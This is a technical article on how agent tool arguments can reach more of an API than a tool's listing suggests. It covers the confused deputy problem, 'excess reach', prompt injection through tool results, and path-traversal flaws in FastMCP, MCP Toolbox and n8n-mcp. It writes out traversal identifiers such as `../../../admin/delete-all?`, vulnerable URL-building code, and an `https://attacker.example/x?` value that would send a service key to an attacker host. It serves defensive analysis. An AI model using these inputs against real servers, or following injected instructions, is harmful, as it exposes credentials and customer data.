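# Agent tools whose text arguments reach more of an API than the tool's name suggests

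## How an agent's tool call becomes an API request

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. Under the working definition in *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026), an agent has access to a language model, runs a loop that turns the model's output into actions, and has tools that act on its surroundings, such as a file system, a browser or a network service. A tool is a function that the model can call. The agent's software gives the model each tool's name, description and input schema, which defines the tool's arguments.

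Many tools do little more than put text from the model into a request to a web service, attach a key and return the response. Someone who approves such a tool relies on its name and description, but what the request does also depends on the text and the key. A tool whose description mentions only one user's profile may return an invoice, or a list of every customer, if the model supplies the right text and the key has permission to read that data.

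### One call, step by step

Suppose a support employee asks an agent which plan customer 42 is on, and the agent has a tool named `get_user_profile`. (The tool is invented, but nothing about it is unusual.)

1. The agent's software sends the question to the model along with the tool registry, the list of tools that the agent, its user or an administrator sees and approves.
2. The model picks a tool and fills in the argument. Its output is a structured call, `get_user_profile(id="42")`.
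3. The agent's software forwards the call to the tool server, the program that carries it out.
4. The tool server's code joins the text `/users/` to the value of `id` to make a path. It then adds the service credential, a key that belongs to the tool server and not to the employee, and sends an HTTP request to the upstream API, the service that holds the customer records.
5. The upstream API checks the key and returns the record. The tool server passes the record back, the model reads it, and the employee gets an answer.

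The request in step 4 looks roughly like this:

```
GET /users/42 HTTP/1.1
Authorization: Bearer SERVICE_CREDENTIAL
```

`GET` is the method, here the HTTP verb for reading, and `/users/42` is the path.

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) attributes the security difficulty to this division of labour. The party that chooses an action (in the example, the model), the user who asked for it (the employee), the program that holds the credential (the tool server) and the service that receives the request (the upstream API) may all be different. The tool server's valid key therefore gives the upstream API very little evidence about whether this employee should get this record for this task.

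### The parts of a tool definition

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic released as open source in November 2024, gives agents and tool servers a common message format. The agent's software sends a `tools/list` request to get a list of a server's tools and a `tools/call` request to use one. Canale and Soulis cite an analysis of 177,436 agent tools that developers created between November 2024 and February 2026. Over that period, tools that change something, rather than only read or compute, rose from 27% to 65% of usage.

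In MCP the example tool might have this definition:

```json
{
  "name": "get_user_profile",
  "description": "Get the profile of one user",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "id": { "type": "string", "description": "The user's ID" }
    },
    "required": ["id"]
  },
  "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true }
}
```

The specification's page on tools, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), defines each part. The `name` identifies the tool, and the `description` explains in ordinary language what it does. The `inputSchema` is a JSON Schema, which specifies the tool's expected arguments and their types in machine-readable form. A definition can also have a display title, icons, an output schema, and `annotations` that describe the tool's behaviour. There is no standard field for the upstream method, path or credential. The schema above requires only that `id`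 be a string, so `"42"` passes, as does any other text. JSON Schema can restrict a string, for example to digits, but the tool's author has to add the restriction.

The annotation `readOnlyHint`, when set to true, means that a tool does not modify its environment. In a 2026 post on the Model Context Protocol blog, the protocol's maintainers describe a typical use, in which a client that trusts the server may skip the confirmation dialog for a tool marked this way. The default is false, and a client should assume that a tool without annotations can make changes, including destructive ones. Many servers ship without any annotations, and the maintainers add that clients differ in how strictly they apply these defaults. The value is a hint from the tool's author, and clients must treat it as untrusted unless they trust the server. The author sets it once for the whole tool, before anyone knows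 what strings the tool will receive.

### What reaches each party

| Party | What it receives | What it does not receive |
|---|---|---|
| Employee | The answer, and perhaps a confirmation prompt that shows the arguments | The HTTP request |
| Model | The conversation, the tool's name, description and schema, and earlier results | The tool server's code and the service credential |
| Tool server | The tool's name and arguments | The conversation, and the reason for choosing 42 |
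| Upstream API | A method, a path and the service credential | The tool's name and description, and usually the employee's identity |

The description of what the tool is supposed to do is in the model's row, and the access needed to do it is in the last row. Only the tool server's code connects the two, and neither the employee nor the model sees that code.

A gateway, a checkpoint that can refuse or alter traffic, can sit at two points on this path. One is between the agent and the tool server, where it receives the tool's name and the arguments as the model wrote them. The July 2026 version of MCP makes this traffic easier to inspect. The sample request in Composio's *The MCP 2026-07-28 Update* carries the tool's name in an HTTP header. The specification also lets a tool's author have clients copy chosen arguments into headers, where a proxy can read them without parsing the message body.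 A network proxy can't see any of this when the tool server runs as a subprocess on the user's machine, because the messages then travel over standard input and output.

A gateway between the tool server and the upstream API receives the finished request, with its method, path and credential. It can read exactly what the tool server is requesting, but nothing in an ordinary HTTP request identifies the tool call that produced it.

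*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) describes three ways to install a check on tool names and arguments: as middleware inside the agent's application, as a separate proxy process on the same machine, or as a central gateway. All three give the same protection, provided that every call with side effects goes through the check.

### Who determines the string

The caller supplies the `id` as a string. The string could have come from at least four sources, and the tool server receives no record of which one.

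The employee may simply have typed 42. An employee can just as easily type the number of a customer whose record they should not see, and the tool server's key will give access to that record too.

The model can also mistakenly put an order number where a customer number belongs, or wrongly reuse a value from an earlier result. Agents routinely depend on the model to copy values from one call's result into the next call. For tools that keep a shopping cart, the MCP specification's guidance is to return an identifier such as `bsk_a1b2c3` and have the model pass it in the next call.

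A third possibility is that no model is involved. An MCP server is a web API that accepts requests from any client able to send them, as PortSwigger's *MCP server vulnerabilities* points out. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (2026) examines servers that obtain authorisation from an upstream service once and then reuse it for every caller. In its example, Facebook authorises a Google-built tool server on the assumption that only Google's agents will use it. If the server is reachable over the network and does not tie the authorisation to a particular caller, an outsider can connect directly and use Google's access. The outsider writes the arguments by hand and can try as many as they like.

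The fourth is an attacker who never touches the tool server but gets the model to write the string for them, which is called prompt injection. David C writes in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, that the flaw arises when developers combine their own instructions with untrusted content in one prompt and rely on the model to keep the two apart. In the indirect form, the attacker has no access to the system and only writes something it will later process, such as a CV with hidden instructions for a screening model to approve the candidate. A language model has no separate channel for instructions and predicts the next token from all the text so far, so David C thinks prompt injection may never have a complete fix.

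Hostile instructions often reach an agent through tool results. Surapani and colleagues note that an agent needs permission to read an email inbox, which is also a source of such instructions. A user profile can also contain them. If customer 42 has written instructions to an AI assistant in the "about me" field, the model reads them in step 5, and its next call to `get_user_profile` may contain a string that the customer chose.

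Models vary widely in how often they follow injected instructions. Mellafe Zuvic reports a benchmark of 27 models in which the injected text presented an unauthorised action as a necessary part of the user's task. On average, the 15 flagship models attempted the action in 19% of trials, and the 12 cheaper models, which a company might choose for high volumes of traffic, in 60%. Single models ranged from 0% (gemini-3.1-pro-preview) to 100% (gpt-4o-mini and glm-4.5-air). Wording also mattered a great deal, with glm-4.7 going from 28% under a crude injection to 100% under one that fitted the task. The sandbox blocked any real effect, so these figures measure attempts rather than breaches. They suggest that developers of tool servers should expect a well-meaning user's agent to send hostile strings at least occasionally.

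The software in between does not usually filter them out. Mellafe Zuvic also audited the public code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. By default, all three restrict which tools the model can call. None checks whether the specific argument values are authorised before the tool runs.

### The confused deputy

In computer security, this situation is called the confused deputy problem. *The Confused Deputy*, a short 1988 paper by Norm Hardy, describes an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX. Users could run it and give the name of a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also collected statistics on how people used the programming language and stored them in (SYSX)STAT, so Tymshare gave it a permission, the "home files license", to write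 to files in SYSX. The company's billing records were in the same directory, in (SYSX)BILL. One day a user gave (SYSX)BILL as the name of the debugging file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had the license, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Each role has a counterpart in the tool call:

| Hardy's story | The tool call |
|---|---|
| The user who supplies a file name | Whoever determines the content of `id` |
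| The file name | The `id` string |
| The compiler | The tool server |
| The home files license | The service credential |
| The operating system | The upstream API |
| (SYSX)STAT, the reason for the licence | User profiles, the reason for the credential |
| (SYSX)BILL | Anything else the credential opens |

Hardy rejects the obvious repairs. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could refuse names in SYSX, but that directory did not exist under that name when the programmers wrote the code, and some people had a right to write to it. It could refuse (SYSX)BILL, but that was not the only sensitive file. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct until Tymshare added the licence. Similarly, a line that joins `/users/` to `id` can be harmless with one key and dangerous with another, and a reviewer who reads only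 the code cannot tell which.

Hardy attributes the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources. It had the user's authority to write the debugging file and its own licence to write the statistics, but it could not specify which one it meant to use. Tymshare patched the problem with a system call that let a program choose between them. A tool server with one shared key cannot use this fix, because the caller brings no separate authority for the server to switch to.

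The tool server attaches the same credential to every request, whatever the path. In *Capability Myths Demolished* (2003), Miller, Yee and Shapiro call this ambient authority, which they describe as "authority that is exercised, but not selected, by its user". They compare it to a world where doors have no keys and open for any visitor judged worthy. They argue that confusion is likely whenever the name of a resource and the permission to use it are passed separately and combined only at the end. Here the caller supplies the name, the tool server's configuration supplies the permission, and the two are combined in the HTTP request.

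Hardy and Miller and colleagues favour capabilities instead. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines a capability as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder may access the object named in it. If the user had needed to give the compiler a ticket for the output file, and not just its name, they could not have supplied one for the billing records. The string `"42"` is only a name. The MCP specification makes the same distinction in its advice on identifiers such as the shopping-cart one ("a handle is a name, not a capability") and recommends that servers with authenticated callers check the caller's authorisation on every call.

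*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) formally defines the confused deputy problem. If R is the set of permitted pairs of party and resource, the problem occurs when a user lacks permission to access a target, (user, target) ∉ R, but the agent accesses it for them because the agent has permission, (agent, target) ∈ R. For example, an employee asks for everyone's salaries and gets them because the agent has administrative access to the personnel database. This definition assumes that the command comes from an authenticated user. In prompt injection, the attacker is the party without permission, and the user may be entitled to everything the agent's key can access.

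The
 request therefore passes through two deputies, the model and then the tool server. David C describes language models as "inherently confusable" and contrasts them with the classical confused deputy, which developers can repair. The tool server is ordinary code and belongs with the classical kind, so its half of the problem seems more hopeful to me.

One partial remedy is least privilege, the principle that every program should run with only the permissions its task requires. If Tymshare had let the compiler write only to (SYSX)STAT in that directory, the billing records would have survived. The company could give `get_user_profile` a key that can only read user profiles, if the upstream API offers one. But Hardy adds that (SYSX)STAT needs protection too, because a user could still have named that file and ruined it. In the same way, a key limited to reading user profiles would still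 let the tool read customer 43's profile.

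## What a tool appears to permit and what it can reach

Returning an invoice from `get_user_profile` is a different fault from returning the wrong customer's profile. Telling the two apart requires comparing what people would expect from the tool's listing with what the tool can do.

### Definitions

The declared scope of a tool t, written S(t), is the set of upstream operations that a reasonable reader would infer from its name, description, schema and annotations. For `get_user_profile`, that is `GET /users/n` for any customer number n. Inferring S(t) takes judgement, and readers may disagree about borderline operations.

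The tool's reach, R(t), depends on the code and the key. Let A(t) be the set of arguments that the tool server accepts, build(a) the request that its code makes from an argument a, and P the set of requests that the upstream API authorises for the service credential. Then:

R(t) = { build(a) : a ∈ A(t) } ∩ P

An operation is in a tool's reach if at least one accepted argument produces it, even if no one has ever sent that argument. Excess reach is R(t) − S(t), the operations in the reach that lie outside the declared scope. If the declared scope includes the whole reach and more, the tool has no excess reach, but it will sometimes fail to do its job.

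A(t) can be larger than the schema suggests. JSON Schema permits undeclared fields unless the schema's author forbids them, and the schema for `get_user_profile` doesn't forbid them. A call with an extra field such as `expand` is valid, so if the server's code copies every field into the request, that field adds to what the tool can reach. *SchemaCaps* (Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee, 2026) studied how tool schemas change between releases of public MCP servers. Of 580 changes that kept all old calls valid, 129 made an object accept undeclared fields.

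The closest published definition concerns files rather than APIs. *My Credentials, Please* (Huang, Tang and colleagues, 2026) defines Reach(t) as all the file reads and writes that a tool t performs on arguments an attacker can steer, and B(t;d) as the permissions that the tool's listing and its deployment d justify. It counts a tool as vulnerable when Reach(t) ⊄ B(t;d). In one of the paper's cases, `git_add` in Anthropic's Git server should have staged files only from a single repository, but it accepted paths containing `../`. It could therefore stage a private SSH key from elsewhere on the machine, and a later call to `git_diff_staged` returned the key's contents.

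R(t) counts every accepted argument, not only those an attacker can influence, because the tool server has no record of who chose the string. S(t) leaves out the deployment because the person approving a tool may have seen only its listing. The `git_add` case also shows a limit of comparing one tool at a time. The comparison detects the read outside the repository but misses the disclosure, which requires a second call to a tool that does nothing unusual.

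Excess reach is also narrower than inaccuracy in general. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, count a tool as inconsistent if its claimed and actual functions differ in either direction, or if it has side effects that its listing leaves out. This includes tools that do less than described. In their opening example, a weather tool also stores the requested city on every call. `get_user_profile`, however, behaves as described for every ordinary ID, so a tester who tries only those will find nothing wrong.

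### The definition applied to `get_user_profile`

Suppose first that the tool server accepts only integers for `id`. Every request it can build then has the form `GET /users/n`. If the key can read all profiles, R(t) equals S(t), so the excess is empty. This depends on the server rejecting all other values, because publishing a schema without enforcing it does not change A(t).

Now suppose that `id` is a string and the server pastes it into the path without encoding it, which would turn characters such as `/` and `?` into harmless data. (The endpoints below are as invented as the tool.)

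| `id` | Request after the API resolves the path | Likely result |
|---|---|---|
| `42` | `GET /users/42` | One profile |
| an empty string | `GET /users/` | On many APIs, a list of all users |
| `42/invoices` | `GET /users/42/invoices` | The customer's invoices |
| `42?include=cards` | `GET /users/42?include=cards` | The profile with payment cards |
| `../admin/export` | `GET /admin/export` | Whatever that endpoint returns |

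In the last row, `..` means "one level up", so the path leaves `/users/`. With enough of these steps, the caller can name any path on the host. The tool can then reach every `GET` operation on that host that the credential allows, although its declared scope has not changed.

Restricting the credential can reduce the tool's reach. If the key can read only profiles, the API refuses requests for invoices and the export, although it may still return the list of all users. But a tool rarely has its own key. *AI Identity* (2026) describes how the tools on an MCP server share its execution context, so a caller can induce a tool meant for low-sensitivity work to act with the server's full privileges. If the same server also offers `get_invoice`, its key must be able to read invoices, and `get_user_profile` uses that key too. A developer who adds a tool and widens the key's permissions can therefore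 give an older tool excess reach without changing its listing or code.

### Which part of the request the caller can write

How much an attacker gains depends on which part of the request the string goes into. The table lists each part separately, on the assumption that the caller controls only that part.

| Part open to the caller | What an attacker gains | What stays fixed |
|---|---|---|
| Method | A different action on the same resource, such as `DELETE /users/42` in place of `GET` | The host and the path, so the damage stays with that resource |
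| Host | The service credential itself, if the tool server attaches it whatever the destination; also a way to contact machines on the internal network | The method and path of this one request, which matter little to someone who now holds the key |
| Path | Other resources and functions of the same API | The method, the host and the body |
| Query | Other options of the same endpoint: more fields, a wider filter, sometimes another account or another action | The method, the host and the path |
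| Body | Other values in whatever the request writes; where an API puts the whole command in the body, any command | The method, the host and the path, which limit very little if every command uses the same address |

More than one row can apply to the same argument. In the example above, one string can set both the path and the query, because a `?` in the path begins the query.

The method stays at `GET` throughout the example. **A fixed `GET` limits the damage only if the API's `GET` operations are harmless.** HTTP defines `GET` as a safe method, meaning that the client isn't asking for anything to change, but the API's developers have to implement it that way, and some don't. Web-based editors have used addresses such as `page?do=delete`, where a crawler deletes pages just by following links. GitLab's *CVE-2026-32871* (2026) describes a path flaw of this kind in FastMCP, a library for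 building MCP servers, and demonstrates it with a `GET` to `/admin/delete-all` on a mock backend.

A request that only reads data can also do serious harm. GitLab's list of possible targets includes endpoints that return API keys and tokens. An attacker who gets such a key can use it directly, with any method it permits.

A `POST` doesn't always change something either. Many APIs use it for plain searches, as the IETF, which develops internet standards, points out in a draft on HTTP queries. Nobody can tell that such a request is only a search without knowing the API. A fixed method is therefore weak evidence that a tool is harmful or that it is harmless, and someone has to go through the API's operations to find out what the tool could do.

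### Four faults that are not excess reach

A tool called `run_sql`, with the description "Run any SQL statement on the customer database", can delete every customer. But this raw-query tool has no excess reach, because its declared scope is as wide as its actual reach. It would have excess reach if it were described as read-only and the server also executed `DELETE` statements. As it stands, an administrator can recognise the danger from the registry and refuse the tool, or give it a key with limited permissions. The tool may still be a bad idea. OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency*, an entry in a list of risks for applications built on language models, advises developers to avoid open-ended tools where possible, such as one that runs a shell command or fetches a URL. OWASP (2026) ranks excessive agency third in the 2026 edition of the list.

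Malicious descriptions are a different problem. In tool poisoning, an attacker hides instructions to the model in a tool's description, for example to read a private file and pass its contents as an argument. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026), a catalogue of 38 threats to MCP systems, lists tool poisoning separately from excessive permissions, confused deputies and path traversal. *Exposed by Design* (2026) likewise separates attacks through the language of tool declarations from faults in servers that pass arguments unsafely to backend systems. Excess reach belongs with the server faults. The developer of `get_user_profile` may be honest, and a scanner checking the tool's description for hostile text will find none, because any hostile text arrives later in the argument.

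An agent can also have too many tools. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Errico, Ngiam and Sojan, 2025) describes a product manager who connects an agent to a data warehouse, two project trackers, email and the customer support system. Even if each tool does only what its listing describes, together they may permit far more than the work requires. The remedy is to remove tools. OWASP recommends offering only the minimum, so that an assistant that summarises a mailbox has no function for deleting or sending messages.

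Removing tools does not reliably prevent excess reach. An administrator might delete `list_all_users` from the registry and believe that the agent can no longer list customers, but it still can if `get_user_profile` accepts an empty string and returns every customer. Decisions based on the registry then rely on an incomplete account of what the agent can do.

In the last fault, which a narrower key does not cure, an employee who may see only customer 42 gets customer 43's record. Security engineers call this broken object level authorisation. *API 01:2023 — Broken object level authorization* illustrates it with an attacker who changes `/api/shop1/financial_info` to `/api/shop2/financial_info` and gets the other shop's figures, because the API does not check permissions. The request applies the right operation to the wrong object, and it is inside S(t) because "get the profile of one user"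 covers customer 43 as well as customer 42. Restricting `id` to integers cures the excess reach but does not prevent this fault. Preventing it requires checking whether this employee may see this record.

Excess reach is closer to the function-level version of that fault. In *API 05:2023 — Broken function level authorization*, an ordinary user moves from `/api/users/v1/user/myinfo` to `/api/admins/v1/users/all`, and the API fails to stop them. A tool with excess reach could send the same request, but the failed check is in a different place. The upstream API may check permissions correctly and still allow the request, because the key it receives has administrative access.

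Whether a request counts as the object-level fault or as excess reach depends on the wording of the tool's listing. If the tool were called `get_my_profile` and its description were "Get the signed-in user's own profile", a request for customer 43 would be outside the declared scope and would count as excess reach, even though the request, code and key were the same.

### Hard cases

Suppose a tool named `search_tickets`, described as "Search support tickets", passes its `query` string to a help desk's search engine. The engine's syntax includes `status:open`, which keeps only open tickets, and `type:user`, which returns customer accounts instead of tickets. Few people who approved the tool would have expected it to return customer accounts.

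Ameur and colleagues devised a test for tool updates that treats an argument as carrying authority if its value can change what the action applies to, where data goes, whose account or tenant is involved, or how the action runs. Filters and page numbers do not carry authority. The test classifies whole arguments, but a search string can contain several operators, so one has to apply the test to each operator. `status:open` is then within the declared scope, while `type:user` is excess reach.

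The answer changes if the description links to the documentation and states that the tool accepts the help desk's full search syntax. A reader can then look up `type:user`, and the tool is close to a raw-query tool for searching. But when the help desk company adds an operator, the tool can immediately reach more, even though the administrator approved it based on the old documentation.

Excess reach is harder to determine for a tool with a name such as `process_data` and a description that adds nothing, because there may be no definite S(t) to subtract. Shi and colleagues treat this vagueness as a fault in its own right. Their example is "process local files", which could mean searching, renaming, compressing or deleting them. If such a listing is read generously, almost any operation falls within the declared scope, and a tool's author could remove excess reach on paper by describing the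 tool less fully. Under a strict reading, nearly everything would be excess, including the tool's ordinary work.

Some operations fall outside any reasonable reading of a tool's listing, and those count as excess reach. For example, few people would expect `process_data` to create an administrator account. It seems better to leave the rest undecided, because the listing gives no basis for approving them. The author should rewrite the listing before anyone tries to measure the gap between what the tool appears to permit and what it can reach.

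Evidence from outside the listing can help establish what the developer intended. Huang and colleagues rank launch settings, documented workspace folders and existing path checks as strong evidence of a tool's intended boundary, and a tool's name as weak evidence. They consider a name like `read_build_log` suggestive but more ambiguous than a configured folder. Of the 13 findings they reported to maintainers, 11 relied on mechanisms in the source code or configuration, and only two on the scope implied by the listing. For an API tool, comparable evidence might be a list of permitted endpoints in the server's settings. Such a list shows what the developer intended, but the person who approved the tool may never have seen it.

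In the remaining case, a tool has an accurate description but a misleading name. Suppose `get_user_profile` had the description "Send a GET request to any path on the customer API". It would have no excess reach under the definition, because S(t) comes from the whole listing and the description is clear. Names alone are an unreliable guide, as Ameur and colleagues found for argument names. A program that judged by name flagged 84 schema changes as adding or widening an argument that carries authority. Human reviewers confirmed 66 and found 10 others that the program had missed.

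But some decisions rely on only part of the listing. An administrator may write a rule that allows every tool whose name begins with `get_`, and a client may skip the confirmation dialog because `readOnlyHint` is true. For those decisions, the tool's reach should be compared with the part the administrator or client relied on. A tool with no excess reach by its full listing can still do far more than the rule's author expected.

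## Identifiers inserted into a URL path

The invented tool `get_user_profile` returns invoices because its server pastes a customer number into a path without encoding it. Real tool servers have had the same fault. Between April and June 2026, vulnerability databases published entries on FastMCP, the library for building MCP servers, Google's MCP Toolbox, and n8n-mcp, a server that lets agents manage workflows on the automation platform n8n. In all three, a caller could use an argument meant for an identifier to send a request, with the service credential attached, to a different endpoint of the same API.

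### FastMCP's URL builder

Many developers describe their web APIs in OpenAPI, a machine-readable format that lists each operation's method, path and parameters. FastMCP's OpenAPIProvider component reads such a description and makes tools from its operations. For example, an operation with the path `/api/v1/users/{id}/profile` becomes a tool with an argument `id`, whose value replaces `{id}` in the path. A developer who leaves administrative operations out of the description would expect agents to be unable to call them.

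The flaw, which has the catalogue number CVE-2026-32871, is in a method named `_build_url`. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-338* (2026), an entry in a database of open-source vulnerabilities, includes the source code. In simplified form, it does this:

```python
url_path = path_template
for name, value in path_params.items():
    url_path = url_path.replace("{" + name + "}", str(value))
return urljoin(base_url.rstrip("/") + "/", url_path.lstrip("/"))
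```

The loop replaces each placeholder with the value exactly as the caller wrote it. The last line removes the slash at the start of the path and passes the rest, along with the API's base address, to `urljoin` from Python's standard library. `urljoin` resolves a relative link such as `../contact` the way a browser does, so it treats `..` as a step up one level.

OSV's demonstration uses the base address `http://127.0.0.1:8080/` and this value for `id`:

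```
../../../admin/delete-all?
```

Substitution gives `/api/v1/users/../../../admin/delete-all?/profile`. `urljoin` splits this at the question mark, so the end of the developer's template, `/profile`, becomes a query string and has no effect on which endpoint receives the request. `urljoin` then goes through the path one segment at a time:

| Segment | Path so far |
|---|---|
| `api` | `/api` |
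| `v1` | `/api/v1` |
| `users` | `/api/v1/users` |
| `..` | `/api/v1` |
| `..` | `/api` |
| `..` | `/` |
| `admin` | `/admin` |
| `delete-all` | `/admin/delete-all` |

The final URL is `http://127.0.0.1:8080/admin/delete-all?/profile`.

Without the question mark, the request would go to `/admin/delete-all/profile`, which does not exist on the test server. A `#` would also work, because HTTP clients don't send the part of a URL that follows it. The attacker doesn't need to know how many levels the template has, since `urljoin` ignores any `..` that would go above the root.

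The expected output in the OSV advisory stops at the question mark and omits `/profile`. The code can't produce that URL, because it never removes the end of the template. The attack works either way, because the test endpoint ignores its query string. But anyone who searches server logs for the exact URL in the advisory will miss real requests. A better search would look for query strings that begin with a slash and match the end of one of the API's own paths.

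On the test server, `/admin/delete-all` returns a message granting administrative access if the request has the header `Authorization: Bearer admin_secret`, and an error otherwise. It doesn't delete anything. OSV's script calls `_build_url` directly and then adds this header itself. The demonstration shows that `_build_url` can produce a URL outside the template, but it doesn't include a complete tool call, in which an earlier check on the arguments might reject the string.

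In an example from FastMCP's API reference, a developer creates one HTTP client and gives it to the provider for the whole API, so a key configured on that client would go out with every tool's requests. The reference also describes the values that go into a request as "Flattened arguments from LLM", which means the model supplies the path parameters.

 NVD, the US government's vulnerability database, likewise describes requests that carry the provider's configured authorisation headers.

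NVD's *CVE-2026-32871 Detail*, published on 2 April 2026, lists the flaw's severity as 10.0, the maximum. GitHub assigned that score, and NVD has not added its own. The score is based on an attacker needing neither an account nor any action by a user, which fits a server that accepts calls from anyone on the network. If the server requires a login or runs on the user's own machine, the attacker must first gain access or get the model to write the string.

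### The check in Google's MCP Toolbox

OSV's *CVE-2026-11720* (2026) describes how an operator configures an HTTP tool in MCP Toolbox with a path such as `/api/v1/users/{{.id}}`. Toolbox inserts the caller's value, parses the result as a relative URL, and checks that the value has not changed the scheme (`http` or `https`), the host, or the user info (a username and password that can precede the host). It then builds the final URL with a function called `ResolveReference`, which works much like Python's `urljoin`.

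A check on the host is worth having. FastMCP's old code has none, and the consequences would be worse for a template that begins with a placeholder, such as `/{tenant}/users`. If the caller gives `https://attacker.example/x?` as the tenant, the code strips the leading slash and passes `urljoin` a complete URL, which `urljoin` returns in place of the API's own. Any key that the HTTP client attaches to all its requests would then go to the attacker.

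But the value `../../../admin/secrets` doesn't change the scheme, host or user info, so it passes the check. `ResolveReference` reduces `/api/v1/users/../../../admin/secrets` to `/admin/secrets`, and Toolbox sends the request there with its configured credentials. The attacker doesn't need a question mark, because this template ends with the placeholder.

Adding the path to the same check might not have helped. Before resolution, the attacker's path still begins with `/api/v1/users/`, so a check that compared only the opening characters would accept it. The comparison has to use the path that Toolbox is about to send. Google fixed the flaw in version 1.3.0.

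### Disabled tools in n8n-mcp

An n8n workflow is an automated sequence of steps across several services, such as copying entries from a web form into a spreadsheet. The n8n-mcp server holds an API key for n8n, and its operator can switch off particular tools with the `DISABLED_TOOLS` setting.

GCVE's *GHSA-8G7G-HMWM-6RV2* (2026), an entry in another vulnerability database, covers versions before 2.50.1. These versions used identifiers from the caller as parts of a URL path without validating them. With a crafted workflow ID, a caller could send a request carrying the n8n key to other endpoints on the same host, despite the operator's `DISABLED_TOOLS` setting. (The same release fixed a separate flaw involving redirects.)

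The setting failed because it controls which tools a caller can name, while the ID determines which endpoint the server contacts. Suppose an operator disables the tool that lists past workflow runs, because those records contain customer data, but keeps a tool enabled that fetches a workflow from `/workflows/{id}`. A caller who asks for the workflow `../executions` makes the server send `GET /executions`, and a log of tool names would show only a permitted tool.

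The HTTP method partly limits what an inserted identifier can do. A tool that always sends `GET` can't replace a disabled tool that needs `DELETE`. But if the operator leaves on a tool for deleting workflows, passing it the ID `../users/5` could delete a user instead, provided the API key allows that. Disabling the tool for deleting users therefore reliably protects them only if the remaining deletion tools validate their identifiers. A key without permission to delete users would protect them even without that validation.

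For operators who cannot upgrade, GCVE suggests restricting network access to trusted callers or running n8n-mcp in stdio mode, which uses standard input and output instead of HTTP. Both workarounds keep outsiders from calling the server directly, but they don't help much against prompt injection, because the model still writes the workflow ID. The advisory's condition that the attacker must be an authenticated caller doesn't limit prompt injection much either, because a misled agent working for a legitimate user meets it.

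The databases classify these closely related flaws differently. NVD lists the FastMCP flaw as server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to send a request of the attacker's choosing. OSV lists the Toolbox flaw as path traversal, in which an attacker escapes an intended directory or path. GitLab's *GHSA-8g7g-hmwm-6rv2* (2026) lists the n8n-mcp advisory under both categories and under exposure of sensitive information. Searching only one of these categories will miss cases.

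### What percent-encoding leaves open

Percent-encoding replaces a character with a percent sign and its hexadecimal code, so that `/` becomes `%2F` and `?` becomes `%3F`. Then software that splits a URL into parts treats the character as data. For FastMCP, OSV recommends passing each value through Python's `quote` function with `safe=""`. By default, `quote` does not encode slashes.

The change blocks the demonstrated attack. The attacker's value becomes `..%2F..%2F..%2Fadmin%2Fdelete-all%3F`, which contains no literal slash or question mark, so `urljoin` treats it as a single user ID between `users` and `profile`.

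OSV also names the full stop among the characters that this fix encodes, which is wrong. `quote` never encodes letters, digits, hyphens, underscores, tildes or full stops, whatever the value of `safe`. A value made up only of dots therefore comes through unchanged:

| `id` | After encoding | Path after resolution |
|---|---|---|
| `42` | `42` | `/api/v1/users/42/profile` |
| `42/x` | `42%2Fx` | `/api/v1/users/42%2Fx/profile` |
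| `..` | `..` | `/api/v1/profile` |
| `.` | `.` | `/api/v1/users/profile` |

An identifier of `..` removes both the placeholder and the segment before it from the path. The attacker can no longer name an endpoint. On OSV's test server, the resulting path, `/api/v1/profile`, does not exist, so the request fails. On another API, the same path might return the profile of the account that owns the key.

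The damage can be greater when the tool makes changes. Suppose a `delete_file` tool sends `DELETE /folders/{folder}/files/{file}`, and the folder is `7`. If the file is `..`, the path `/folders/7/files/..` resolves to `/folders/7/`, and an API that ignores the final slash may delete the folder. If the file is `.`, the path resolves to `/folders/7/files/`, and some APIs will delete every file in the folder.

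If a template has adjacent placeholders, an attacker regains some choice over which path the request reaches. In `/api/v1/projects/{project}/{item}`, a caller can set the project to `..` and the item to `users`, so the path resolves to `/api/v1/users`. The caller can replace `users` with any other single segment.

These results are for OSV's sample code and don't establish that FastMCP 3.2.0 has the same gap. FastMCP's release notes describe the fix only as URL-encoding path parameters. If the shipped code does no more than that, `..` still works. The notes for *v4.2.0* list a later fix to how the library writes path parameters into URLs. An operator can check an installed version by calling a tool with the ID `..` against a test server and reading the path in the server's log.

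The tool server has to refuse values such as `..`. Encoding the dots by hand as `%2E` is unreliable because RFC 3986, the internet standard for URL syntax, treats `%2E` and `.` as equivalent and lets software convert one into the other. The URL parser in browsers and Node.js treats `%2e%2e` as `..`. Replacing `urljoin` with simple concatenation in FastMCP would not have been enough either, because httpx, the HTTP client in OSV's demonstration, resolves `..` before it sends a request.

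### Upstream servers that decode the slash

An encoded slash protects the path only if every program that handles the request treats it as data. Some web servers decode the path before choosing the endpoint, so they treat `/users/42%2Finvoices` and `/users/42/invoices` as the same request.

FastAPI, which OSV uses for its test server, matches routes against a path that the web server has already decoded. Suppose a tool has the template `/api/v1/users/{id}` and a caller supplies `42/profile`. Correct encoding produces `/api/v1/users/42%2Fprofile`, but FastAPI still matches it to the profile endpoint, so the caller reaches a different operation without using any dots.

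Going up a level also requires something to resolve the `..` after decoding. FastAPI does not do that, but a proxy in front of it may. The web server nginx decodes the path and resolves dot segments before matching the path against its rules. A request for `/api/v1/users/..%2F..%2F..%2Fadmin%2Fexport` can therefore fall under the rules for `/admin/`. The path nginx passes to the application depends on nginx's configuration.

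OSV's original payload would still fail on such a server. The server separates the query string before it decodes the path, so a decoded `%3F` is an ordinary character and `/profile` stays in the path. An attacker would need a template that ends with the placeholder, or an endpoint whose path ends with the text that follows the placeholder.

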